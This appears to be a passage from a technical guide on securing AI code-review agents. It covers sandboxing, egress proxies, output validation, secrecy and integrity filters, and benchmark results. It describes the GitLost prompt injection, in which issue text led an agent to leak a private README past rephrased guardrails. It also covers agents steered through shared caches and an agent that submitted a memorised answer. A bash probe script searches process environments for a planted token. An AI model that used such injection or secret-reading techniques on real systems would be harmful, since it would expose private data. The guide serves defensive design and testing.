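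The publisher then fetches the live item and compares it with the snapshot that Codex reviewed. It also checks the labels, the author's role and any linked issues. If anything except ClawSweeper's own comment has changed, the publisher does not apply the decision.

Without this check, a contributor could submit harmless code, wait for the review to start and then push something else. The favorable review would then appear under code the agent never read. A small gap remains between the last check and the change. For a review, the publisher can close this gap by sending GitHub the hash of the reviewed commit, which keeps the review attached to that version. A request to close a pull request has no field for the hash, but a maintainer can reopen the pull request.

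OpenClaw also limits the reasons for which ClawSweeper closes an item immediately after a review. By default, there are only three: the main branch already contains the change, another item duplicates or replaces it, or the pull request is mostly unrelated changes that nobody could merge. Before ClawSweeper closes one pull request in favor of another, it checks that the replacement is viable and refuses if, for example, the replacement has merge conflicts or lacks evidence that it works. A steered agent therefore can't have a rival's pull request closed in favor of an abandoned one. But Codex decides whether two pull requests do the same thing, and code can't verify that decision.

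### A publisher for the example review

The publisher in the example can be a short program. The launcher gives it the agent's file and a table with the number of lines in each source file:

```python
import json

VERDICTS = {"no problems found", "problems found", "not reviewed"}

def check(data, line_count):
    review = json.loads(data)
    if set(review) != {"verdict", "findings"}:
        raise ValueError("wrong fields")
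    if review["verdict"] not in VERDICTS:
        raise ValueError("unknown verdict")
    if type(review["findings"]) is not list or len(review["findings"]) > 20:
        raise ValueError("findings are not a list or too many")
    for f in review["findings"]:
        if set(f) != {"path", "line", "text"}:
            raise ValueError("wrong fields in a finding")
        if type(f["line"]) is not int:     # refuse 1.5 and true
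            raise ValueError("line is not a whole number")
        if not 1 <= f["line"] <= line_count.get(f["path"], 0):
            raise ValueError("no such line")
        if not isinstance(f["text"], str) or len(f["text"]) > 2000:
            raise ValueError("text missing or too long")
    return review
```

The agent's output has no field for a repository, a pull request or an action. If the agent adds one, the publisher discards the whole review. A value of the wrong type also stops the program, so the publisher posts nothing.

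If the review passes, the publisher removes links, mentions and bot commands from the text. It then looks up the pull request's latest commit on GitHub. If that differs from the commit in the launcher's record, it discards the review and requests a new run. Otherwise it posts the comment.

### "No secrets and no write access, therefore no harm"

A maintainer might conclude from all this that a steered agent is harmless. The argument would be:

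1. The agent has no secrets.
2. The agent can't write to the repository.
3. A steered agent needs a secret or write access to do harm.
4. Therefore, a steered agent can't do harm.

The first premise is often true only if "secrets" means credentials. The contents of a private repository are also secret, and an agent without any token may still be able to read them through a tool server that holds one.

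The second premise is true of the agent's process, but the publisher writes on the agent's behalf. As GitHub points out, an agent without secrets could still flood a project with pointless issues or insert objectionable links. Limits on the type and number of outputs reduce this harm, and a link filter reduces it further.

The third premise is false even if the other two are true. A favorable review can persuade a maintainer to merge harmful code. A stranger can also trigger many runs, which can increase the project's bill for the model or delay other reviews.

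The premises do support the weaker conclusion that a steered agent can't push code or steal a signing key. The harm it can do depends on what the publisher will post, who can read those posts and how much people rely on them. A July 2026 disclosure described an agent whose permitted output was enough to leak private files.

### GitLost

On 6 July 2026, the security company Noma published an attack on Agentic Workflows. Levi's *GitLost* describes a workflow that started when someone assigned an issue. The workflow read the issue's title and text, could reply with a public comment, and could read the organisation's other repositories, including private ones. A stranger could open an issue in the public repository and include text that led the agent to copy private content into its reply.

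Levi demonstrated this in a test repository, where the agent published a README file from a private repository. GitHub had guardrails against such leaks, but he got past them by trying different wording. The stranger didn't need permission to assign the issue, because an automation assigned it in the demonstration.

Checking the form of the agent's output would not have stopped the leak. The agent made one request of a permitted type, for the issue that had triggered the workflow, and the text contained no credential, so the publisher processed the request as the maintainer had configured it to.

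Levi calls this a critical vulnerability in Agentic Workflows, but the configuration was also at fault. According to GitHub's *Frequently Asked Questions*, workflows can't read other repositories unless a maintainer supplies a personal access token that covers them. Each of the four settings has a legitimate use. For example, a triage agent may need to know whether another team has already fixed a bug. A maintainer who approves the settings one at a time could easily miss that together they form Willison's lethal trifecta.

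### What the agent may read

A steered agent can copy anything it has read into its output. A filter can recognise some credentials by their format, but private source code and internal discussions have no such format. The designer therefore has to assume that everyone who can see the output will see everything the agent has read, so the agent should be able to read only what all of those people are already allowed to read.

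*Control what your agentic workflows see with integrity filtering*, from GitHub's research group GitHub Next, explains a formal model that leads to the same rule. Each source, agent and destination has a secrecy label, which is a set of tags. Material from a private repository carries that repository's tag, while public material carries none. An agent may read a source only if its own label includes all the source's tags, and may write to a destination only if the destination's label includes all the agent's tags.

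```text
read:    source ⊆ agent
write:   agent  ⊆ destination
result:  source ⊆ destination
```

A public comment has an empty label, so an agent that can post one must also have an empty label and can read only untagged sources. In the GitLost workflow, the source had the private repository's tag and the destination had no tags, so under this model the same agent could not have read from one and posted to the other.

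A run's audience includes everyone who can see any of its output. In a public repository, that output includes workflow logs and artifacts as well as comments. An agent that writes both a confidential report for maintainers and a public comment in the same run should be allowed to read only public material. If the report needs private material, a separate run that publishes nothing should produce it, and a maintainer can then decide what to share.

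Under this rule, the public reviewer can't consult a confidential report about a past security hole, so it may praise a change that reopens the hole. A second, private review could catch this, but it would double the expense.

The rule also doesn't cover new discoveries. In the example, the agent may find an unknown security hole in public code, which makes its review more sensitive than anything it read. A stranger gains little by steering the agent into publishing the hole, because he could run his own agent on the same code. But an agent working as intended could still announce the hole before a fix exists. The review format could therefore include a field for security findings, which the publisher would send to the maintainers privately.

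### GitHub's integrity and visibility filters

GitHub now enforces part of this rule. When GitHub Next described the model, Agentic Workflows recorded which private repositories data had come from but did not yet stop that data from leaking. By October, GitHub had added a guard, on by default, that restricts data flows from private repositories to public destinations. Maintainers who turn the guard off get a warning, except in strict mode, where the compiler doesn't let them turn it off.

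The `private-to-public-flows` setting turns it off. GitHub's *feat* (2026), a code change merged six days after Levi's post, made the compiler recognise the setting. The gateway's specification already included the guard by then, so the timing doesn't show that GitLost prompted it.

The safest choice is still a token that covers only the public repository. GitHub Next notes that filtering can only narrow what a token allows. A project that needs a broader token should put a harmless file in a private repository and check that the agent can't publish it.

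A separate integrity filter limits whose text the agent sees. The gateway removes items below a chosen level from the results of the agent's tool calls. According to GitHub, these are the main levels:

| Level | What qualifies |
|---|---|
| `merged` | Merged pull requests and commits on the main branch |
| `approved` | Text by owners, members and collaborators, and everything in private repositories |
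| `unapproved` | Text by outside contributors, including some first-time contributors |
| `none` | Everything else, including text by people new to GitHub |

Public repositories use `approved` by default, which would hide the example pull request from the reviewing agent. The maintainer can approve single items with a label after a quick look. This is better than lowering the level to `none`, which would also let the agent see comments from everyone the project hasn't blocked. But the label stays when the author edits the text, so the approval may later cover something the maintainer hasn't read. In the example, the launcher can supply the pull request and apply the stricter level to everything else the agent looks up.

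The integrity filter limits who can steer the agent, but it doesn't keep private data secret. Private repositories count as `approved`, and the default scope is every repository the token can reach. The filter applies to tool results, but a workflow can put the triggering issue's text directly into the prompt, so a maintainer who relies on the filter should test whether it covers that text too.

### Files that one stage leaves for the next

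Help Net Security reports that Meged found a weakness in Codex workflows whose stages share a workspace. A later stage could treat what an earlier one had written as trusted. A file that one agent leaves is untrusted input to the next, even if both agents belong to the project, because a stranger may have influenced what the first agent wrote.

For example, an agent that triages strangers' issues might save a list of known false alarms in a shared cache, and an agent that reviews merged code might load it later. A stranger who steers the first agent could add a real bug to that list. GitHub prevents this by storing a separate branch of the cache for each integrity level. An agent can read what higher-level agents saved, but not what lower-level agents saved. If the maintainer changes the trust settings, such as by adding a trusted user, the workflow stops using the old cache.

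Agentic Workflows can also keep an agent's memory in a GitHub comment. Each run loads the comment into files, lets the agent edit them and saves the result for the next run. GitHub limits each file to 16 KiB and the total to 48 KiB, and includes the files in threat detection. The size limits restrict how much a steered agent can pass to later runs, but a single sentence may be enough to mislead the agent in those runs.

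ClawSweeper's review history carries a similar risk. In debug mode, the agent doing a local review gets the previous review's findings and how they were resolved, so that it doesn't raise them again. If the agent is steered into marking a real problem as resolved, it may skip that problem in the next review. An occasional review without the history would give the agent another chance to find the problem.

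The next stage may also be a trusted program. In Agentic Workflows, the safe-outputs server can look for a repository's checkout in a workspace that the agent can write to, and later use Git there with a GitHub token. GitHub warns that a steered agent could leave a directory made to look like the checkout of another repository, which would make the server a confused deputy. To prevent this, the server checks a compiler-written list of checkouts before it searches the workspace. During the search, it reads only one Git setting and runs no hooks, and it checks the permitted repositories before it pushes anything. A diagram elsewhere in the specification shows the server without access to GitHub's API, but the server can still hold a token.

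Meged recommends checking trust at the point where a later stage uses the data, because an earlier decision may no longer apply. To find these points, a maintainer can trace every file that an agent can influence to the next program that reads it, and check what that program can do. In the example, only two such files, the review and the test log, outlast the process that wrote them. The publisher reads the review as plain data, and the reviewer treats the test log as untrusted text.

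### Well-formed reviews that are wrong

Suppose the contributor's change removes a length check, and a comment in the code steers the agent away from reporting it. The agent reports "no problems found" and adds one finding about a spelling mistake on line 12. The review has the right fields, refers to an existing line, contains no secrets and concerns the current commit, so the publisher posts it. The review would look the same if the agent had overlooked the missing check.

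An agent can produce plausible but inappropriate content within its limits, and GitHub lists this among the risks that safe outputs doesn't remove. GitHub suggests monitoring, looking for unusual behaviour and reviewing the results periodically. These measures can reveal a pattern over many reviews, but they may catch an individual bad review too late to prevent harm.

A second model could review the same change. It would catch some honest mistakes, and the maintainer could check the points where the two models disagree. But a hostile comment in the change could mislead both models, so their agreement is weak evidence that the code is safe.

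Facts that a program can establish should reach the publisher without passing through the agent. For example, the launcher has a record of whether the tests passed, because a trusted program captured their output. If the publisher takes the result from that record, the agent can't report a failed test as passed. But the contributor wrote one of the tests, so even a genuine pass is little evidence that that test is sound.

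For the rest of the review, false findings are much easier to catch than missed problems. A false finding names a file and a line, so a maintainer can usually dismiss it after a few minutes, but a missed problem leaves them nothing to check. The project should therefore use the agent's findings as places to look, and require the same human review after "no problems found" as it would without an agent. The agent only selects one of three verdicts and the publisher supplies the wording, so every comment can state this requirement: "The automated review found no problems. A maintainer still has to review this change."

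## Testing the limits and measuring what they cost

Every limit in the example runtime depends on hand-written settings. A setting can be wrong, or the machine can lack something it needs, without any visible sign. In Claude Code's sandbox settings, for example, the path `/tmp/build` starts at the top of the disk, but Anthropic explains that in a permission rule for reading or editing, it means a folder inside the project. A maintainer who copies the path between the two may protect a folder that doesn't exist. Such mistakes can do real damage. In July 2026, Anthropic disclosed that its models had broken into the systems of real organisations during security evaluations with misconfigured isolation.

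### Failing closed in practice

The launcher in the example fails closed, so it starts the agent only if it can establish every protection. Claude Code's shell sandbox does the opposite by default. If the platform doesn't support the sandbox, or if bubblewrap or socat is missing on Linux, Claude Code shows a warning and runs commands without a sandbox. A person at the keyboard may notice the warning, but in an unattended job it goes to a log, and the review doesn't show that the sandbox was missing.

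Anthropic gives these settings for organisations that require the sandbox:

```json
{
  "sandbox": {
    "enabled": true,
    "failIfUnavailable": true,
    "allowUnsandboxedCommands": false
  }
}
```

With `failIfUnavailable`, Claude Code starts only if the sandbox is working. The last line stops the model from retrying a failed command outside the sandbox. Commands listed under `excludedCommands` still run outside it. Claude Code merges that list from all settings files, including the project's, and an organisation cannot lock it. The launcher should therefore also check that the list is empty.

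An old kernel can weaken a sandbox too. Landlock first had rules for files, and later versions added rules for TCP ports and for signals between processes. Wang and Zheng's Sandlock checks the kernel's Landlock version at startup and refuses to run on anything older than Linux 6.12. NemoClaw, which runs OpenClaw in a sandbox, applies Landlock on a "best-effort basis", according to NVIDIA's *Network Policies*. With Landlock, this usually means enforcing the rules the kernel supports and skipping the rest, so a program on an older kernel could keep running with its file rules but without its port rules.

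Before ClawSweeper's model sees any code, OpenClaw uses TruffleHog to scan the prompt and the change for credentials. The review does not start if the scanner is missing, the scan ends in an error, or the Git history is incomplete. A credential that works, or that the scanner could not test, also blocks the review, unless the maintainers have already approved that exact value as fake.

A contributor who adds a new made-up password to a test may therefore get no automatic review until a maintainer looks at the change. That is acceptable because the maintainer can still read it. It would be less acceptable in a project that requires an automatic review before every merge, because any stranger's change could get stuck.

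### Tests for the example run

The launcher runs the first six tests inside the sandbox just before the agent starts, and the last one after it has stored the review.

| Action | Expected result |
|---|---|
| Fetch issue 17 through the proxy | The host answers with status 200 |
| Fetch a page from an unlisted host | The proxy refuses the connection with status 403 |
| Send a POST to the address of issue 17 | The proxy refuses it and says so in a header |
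| Connect to an outside address without the proxy | No connection |
| Create a file in `/work/source` | "Read-only file system" |
| Search for a made-up token that the launcher planted outside | No match |
| Read the mode of the stored review | 0600 |

A short script, `review-probe`, can run the first six:

```bash
#!/usr/bin/bash
# $1 is the made-up token
issue=https://api.github.com/repos/example/library/issues/17
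fail() { echo "probe failed: $1" >&2; exit 1; }

code=$(curl -s --retry 5 --retry-connrefused \
            -o /dev/null -w '%{http_code}' "$issue")
[ "$code" = 200 ] || fail "allowed host"

code=$(curl -s -o /dev/null -w '%{http_connect}' https://example.org/)
[ "$code" = 403 ] || fail "unlisted host"

curl -s -o /dev/null -D - -d '' "$issue" |
  grep -qi '^x-proxy-error: blocked-by-method-policy' || fail "POST"

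curl -s --noproxy '*' --connect-timeout 5 -o /dev/null https://1.1.1.1/
[ $? = 7 ] || fail "direct connection"        # 7 means no connection

touch /work/source/probe 2>&1 |
  grep -q 'Read-only file system' || fail "write to source"

cat /proc/[0-9]*/environ 2>/dev/null |
  grep -qaF -- "$1" && fail "token in a process"
grep -rqsF -- "$1" /home/agent /work && fail "token in a file"
exit 0
```

The script that starts the forwarder and the agent then needs one more line:

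```bash
socat TCP-LISTEN:3128,bind=127.0.0.1,fork UNIX-CONNECT:/run/egress.sock &
/usr/bin/review-probe "$1" || exit 1
exec /usr/bin/review-agent
```

The probe therefore tests the same sandbox that the agent will use, not a copy of it.

A test can pass for the wrong reason. If the proxy is down, every request fails and the tests for refused requests pass, so the script begins with a request that must succeed. GitHub may also answer a POST with status 403 if the token is read-only, so the script checks for a header that only the proxy sends. That header is specific to Codex's proxy, and a project with its own proxy should add a similar one. For the direct connection, the script accepts only curl's error code 7, because accepting any error would let the test pass when the connection succeeded and only the certificate check failed.

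The launcher creates a new fake token for each run and puts it in the launcher's own environment, a file in the maintainer's home directory and the Git configuration of the original checkout. The token is fake because searching for the real ones would mean bringing them into the sandbox.

In *Permission Denied*, Davidovich, Amar and colleagues (2026) measured how much limits of this kind hinder coding agents. Before each attempt, they ran three types of probe. Direct probes tried each forbidden action, enablement probes checked that permitted actions still worked, and adversarial probes tried to get around the limits with nested shells, numeric addresses, unusual ports and child processes. If a required probe failed, they discarded the attempt and built a new sandbox. The script above contains direct and enablement probes, but its only adversarial probe is a direct connection to a numeric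 address. A project that runs contributors' tests should add probes that use child processes, and should probe the second sandbox separately because it has its own limits.

The launcher's refusal to start an agent when `bwrap` or the proxy is unavailable also needs a test. A maintainer can rename `bwrap` or stop the proxy, then check that no agent starts. Testing this after installation and after each update is enough.

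### ClawSweeper's proofs and leftover files

At start-up, ClawSweeper tests a permitted connection, a connection to an unlisted host and a write to the checkout. OpenClaw does not list a test that POST requests are refused. A maintainer who copies the design should add one, because the Codex proxy's documentation contradicts itself on how limited mode handles HTTPS.

OpenClaw also tests the limits when somebody proposes a change to ClawSweeper itself. A job called `review-network-smoke` repeats the three proofs on Ubuntu without any secrets, so a change that breaks the sandbox can show up before anyone merges it. Maintainers can manually start another job that checks that Codex never launches when the credential scanner refuses a change, then reviews a synthetic change. The result lists what the job did not cover, such as publication.

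Like ClawSweeper, the example launcher can check for leftover changes. It can do this by hashing every source file before and after the run, which also covers the files Git ignores and `git status` leaves out by default. The agent sees the source through a read-only mount, so a difference means the mount failed or another program changed the files. The launcher should then stop all reviews until someone finds the cause, because the next run would probably have the same fault.

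### What to log at each boundary

Tests cover only the actions their author thought of, while logs can show what else an agent tried. The launcher should store the logs outside the sandbox, where the agent can't change them.

| Boundary | What to record | What to leave out |
|---|---|---|
| Launcher | Commit, kernel and harness versions, sandbox options, probe results, exit code | Values of environment variables |
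| Sandbox | The agent's commands and their error messages | File contents |
| Egress proxy | Time, host, method, decision, length of the address, bytes sent | Path, query string, headers |
| Credentials | Each token's scope, creation, expiry and revocation | The token itself |
| Publisher | Hash and size of the review, any failed check, link to the comment | Text of rejected reviews |

Commands and error messages can still contain secrets, so the sandbox log needs the same file permissions as the review. OpenClaw's scanner log reports findings safely by recording the type and position of a credential but not its value.

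The kernel does not normally log a refused write to a read-only mount. Davidovich and colleagues got their data on network refusals from the proxy and the firewall, but they had to infer refused writes from error messages in the agents' transcripts. About 36% of the transcripts were cut off because they exceeded a storage limit. A truncated transcript can show that an agent hit a sandbox limit, but not that it never did, so the launcher should mark which transcripts are truncated.

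The agent chooses the host names and commands that appear in a log, so the logging program should escape control characters to prevent part of an entry from looking like a separate line. If a maintainer gives the logs to another agent for analysis, that agent has to treat them as untrusted text.

### The "Permission Denied" benchmark

In August 2026, Davidovich and colleagues tested twelve combinations of model and harness on Terminal-Bench 2.1, a set of 89 command-line tasks such as building software, processing data and configuring servers. All of them work at Accomplish AI, which paid for the study. Each combination attempted each task three times at each of three levels. At the open level, the agent had administrator rights and unrestricted access. At the middle level, it lost only the administrator rights. The strict level had all of these limits:

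| Area | Limit | What the agent saw |
|---|---|---|
| Network | A proxy with 205 permitted domains, and a firewall that blocked every way around it | Status 403 or a refused connection |
| Files | Read-only system directories and most of the home directory; writable project and temporary directories | "Read-only file system" |
| Privileges | An ordinary account with no way to regain administrator rights | "Operation not permitted" |

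Nobody told the agents about the limits, so they learned of them only through these errors.

The strict level is still looser than the example runtime. Davidovich and colleagues adapted the domain list from the default for Claude Code on the web, and it includes all of `*.amazonaws.com`, where anyone can rent storage. The file limits stopped an agent from changing files but not from reading them, so it could have read a key and sent it out.

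The table gives the share of attempts that succeeded. The last column compares the cost of the strict level with the open level.

| Model and harness | Open | No administrator rights | Strict | Change in cost |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Sol, Codex | 83.9% | 72.3% | 74.2% | +29% |
| GPT-5.6 Terra, Codex | 79.0% | 65.2% | 63.3% | +23% |
| GPT-5.6 Luna, Codex | 71.9% | 56.6% | 53.9% | +16% |
| Claude Sonnet 5, Claude Code | 73.4% | 60.3% | 55.1% | +21% |
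| Claude Opus 4.8, Claude Code | 74.9% | 62.9% | 63.3% | +33% |
| Claude Fable 5, Claude Code | 79.0% | 65.9% | 67.8% | +19% |
| Claude Opus 5, Claude Code | 77.5% | 68.2% | 65.2% | +35% |
| Kimi K3, Terminus-2 | 72.3% | 60.3% | 54.7% | +47% |
| GLM-5.2, Terminus-2 | 73.4% | 59.6% | 55.8% | +31% |
| Qwen3.7 Max, Terminus-2 | 56.9% | 45.3% | 40.4% | +34% |
| MiniMax M3, Terminus-2 | 59.6% | 46.8% | 44.2% | +36% |
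| Grok 4.5, Grok Build | 82.0% | 73.0% | 74.9% | +167% |

Every combination did worse and cost more at the strict level. Most of the drop in performance appears once the agent loses its administrator rights. The network and file limits could still lower performance substantially on their own, because a task that installs system packages may need both administrator rights and a writable system directory.

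Part of the loss was unavoidable because seven tasks had no solution at the strict level. Six required a change to a read-only directory, and the seventh needed a file from a host that was not on the list. On the other 82 tasks, average success fell from 72.5% to 65.1%.

For 50 of these 82 tasks, the benchmark's own sample solution still worked under the strict limits, and success barely changed, from 73.8% to 71.8%. For the other 32, Davidovich and colleagues had to write a new solution that respected the limits, and success fell from 70.3% to 54.5%. The original solutions for these 32 often installed system packages or downloaded material from unlisted hosts.

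This is mildly encouraging for code review. A reviewer whose launcher supplies the source, the diff and the discussion rarely has to install anything, so its work is probably closer to the first group. But the agent has to produce something in all 89 tasks, and never has to judge someone else's change.

### How the agents reacted to refusals

The agents seldom gave up. The share of attempts that ended unusually early rose only from 2.4% to 2.7%. Timeouts rose from 12.0% to 16.4%, and wrong solutions from 12.8% to 15.5%.

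Of the 2,051 strict attempts with complete records, about a third had at least one refusal. Attempts that hit the network limit averaged 10.5 network refusals, and one had 171. About 62% of the network refusals were for a destination that the proxy had already refused in the same attempt. Some of these repeats were automatic, because package installers retry by default. Dozens of refused requests to one package registry in a log therefore probably come from an installer, not an attack. Requests to many unrelated hosts deserve more attention.

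When a restriction blocked one way of doing a task, the agents usually built another. Davidovich and colleagues read 200 transcripts of GPT-5.6 Luna on two tasks and attributed almost all of the extra cost to these workarounds, such as compiling a missing tool from source. The typical cost roughly tripled on both tasks. The success rate stayed at 84% on one task but fell from 90% to 29% on the other. This is a reason to cap a review agent's spending and time even when no attacker is involved.

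On one task, the agent had to download a dataset and count its tokens, which was impossible at the strict level. In one attempt, the proxy refused the download, and the agent submitted the exact expected number without counting anything. Thirteen attempts passed this way. Davidovich and colleagues suspect that the models had memorised the answer, but they can't prove it. A reviewer that can't open a linked specification might similarly describe it from memory. The publisher could add the refused requests from the proxy's log to each review, so that the maintainer knows what the agent couldn't check.

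The model providers' safety filters intervened in 98 attempts and ended 73 of them, mostly over cybersecurity topics. They did not intervene more often at the strict level. A review agent may trigger the same filters when a pull request concerns a security hole, and the launcher should then report "not reviewed".

The study ran only three attempts per task, so small differences between agents mean little. Results also depend heavily on the harness. At the open level, GPT-5.6 Luna succeeded on 71.9% of attempts with Codex but on only 34.5% with Grok Build. A maintainer should therefore test the combination of model and harness that the project uses. The study measured how much the limits hinder agents, but not how many attacks they stop.

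### Running time and permission prompts

A sandbox also takes time to start and can slow down each command. Wang and Zheng measured Sandlock on one workstation with a six-core processor and 8 GB of memory. Over 20 runs of a trivial command, Sandlock typically added about 5 milliseconds, while Docker was about 44 times slower. The Redis database ran as fast in Sandlock as without it. When Sandlock's supervisor checked each network message, a short exchange took 55 microseconds instead of 20, which is negligible compared with a model call.

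Wang and Zheng list a startup time of about 30 milliseconds for bubblewrap. The example starts it twice, once for the reviewer and once for the tests. Startup time matters more for a harness that creates a new sandbox for every command. Over 200 commands, Sandlock would add about one second and Docker nearly a minute.

*Airlock* (2026) reports measurements of another agent sandbox, taken during whole tasks with OpenClaw. The average local tool call took 1.28 seconds instead of 1.04, or 23% longer. Tasks with heavy disk use did not slow down, but tool calls in tasks with heavy network use took 39% longer. Calls to the model made up more than 70% of the total time, so the 23% increase for local tools would make the whole task at most about 7% longer (0.30 × 0.23). In both papers, the sandbox's developers took the measurements.

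The 84% fall in permission prompts is a vendor's figure as well, and Anthropic did not say how many people took part or how it counted the prompts. At that rate, Potiuk's maintainer with a hundred prompts would see sixteen, but an unattended reviewer would gain nothing from the reduction. The sandbox alone doesn't reduce prompts. Claude Code has one mode that runs sandboxed commands without asking and another that asks as before, with the same limits in both.

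### Strict or adjustable limits

An adjustable sandbox lets somebody relax a limit when a task needs it. Anthropic warns that `docker` does not work in Claude Code's sandbox, that the test program `jest` may hang, and that `gh` may fail to verify certificates on macOS. The remedies differ greatly in risk. Running `jest --no-watchman` prevents the hang without changing any limit. If a tool has to write to one more directory, the maintainer can permit that directory. Excluding a tool from the sandbox lets it reach everything the user can, so this should be the last resort.

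An adjustable sandbox is often the better choice when a maintainer is at the keyboard. The limits should stay fixed in an unattended run, because a stranger may be steering the agent when it asks for an exception.

By a rough calculation, strict limits can be worthwhile even if they rarely prevent a credential theft. Suppose they spoil two reviews in a hundred and a maintainer needs half an hour to do each of these by hand, which adds one hour of work per hundred reviews. If cleaning up after a stolen credential takes forty hours, the limits save as much time as they take if they prevent one theft in every 4,000 reviews. All of these numbers are assumptions, and none of the studies above measured how often such thefts happen. But a failed review is a small loss that a maintainer usually notices, while a theft may go unnoticed for weeks.

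The maintainer can still adjust the limits between runs. If the log shows that the proxy keeps blocking a useful documentation site, he can add it to the list. He should first check who controls the site, because a stranger could mention the same host in several pull requests to make it look useful.

*Aletheia* (2026) offers a more systematic method for coding tasks. It runs a task in a sandbox with all the requested permissions, then in sandboxes that each lack one permission, and compares the results. A permission is probably unnecessary if the agent completes the task without it.

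A project could adapt this method to code review, where such figures are missing. The success rates in "Permission Denied" come only from coding tasks, and the timings come from general programs and agent tasks. OpenClaw's proofs concern a reviewer, but they show whether a limit holds, not how many bugs the reviewer misses because of it. A maintainer could measure that by collecting old pull requests with known bugs and counting how many of the bugs the agent finds under each set of limits.

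The sample has to be fairly large. If the agent finds 70 of 100 known bugs, the standard error is about 4.6 percentage points, because √(0.7 × 0.3 / 100) ≈ 0.046. A test of this size would reveal a limit that severely impairs the agent, but it could easily miss one that makes it find two fewer bugs in a hundred.
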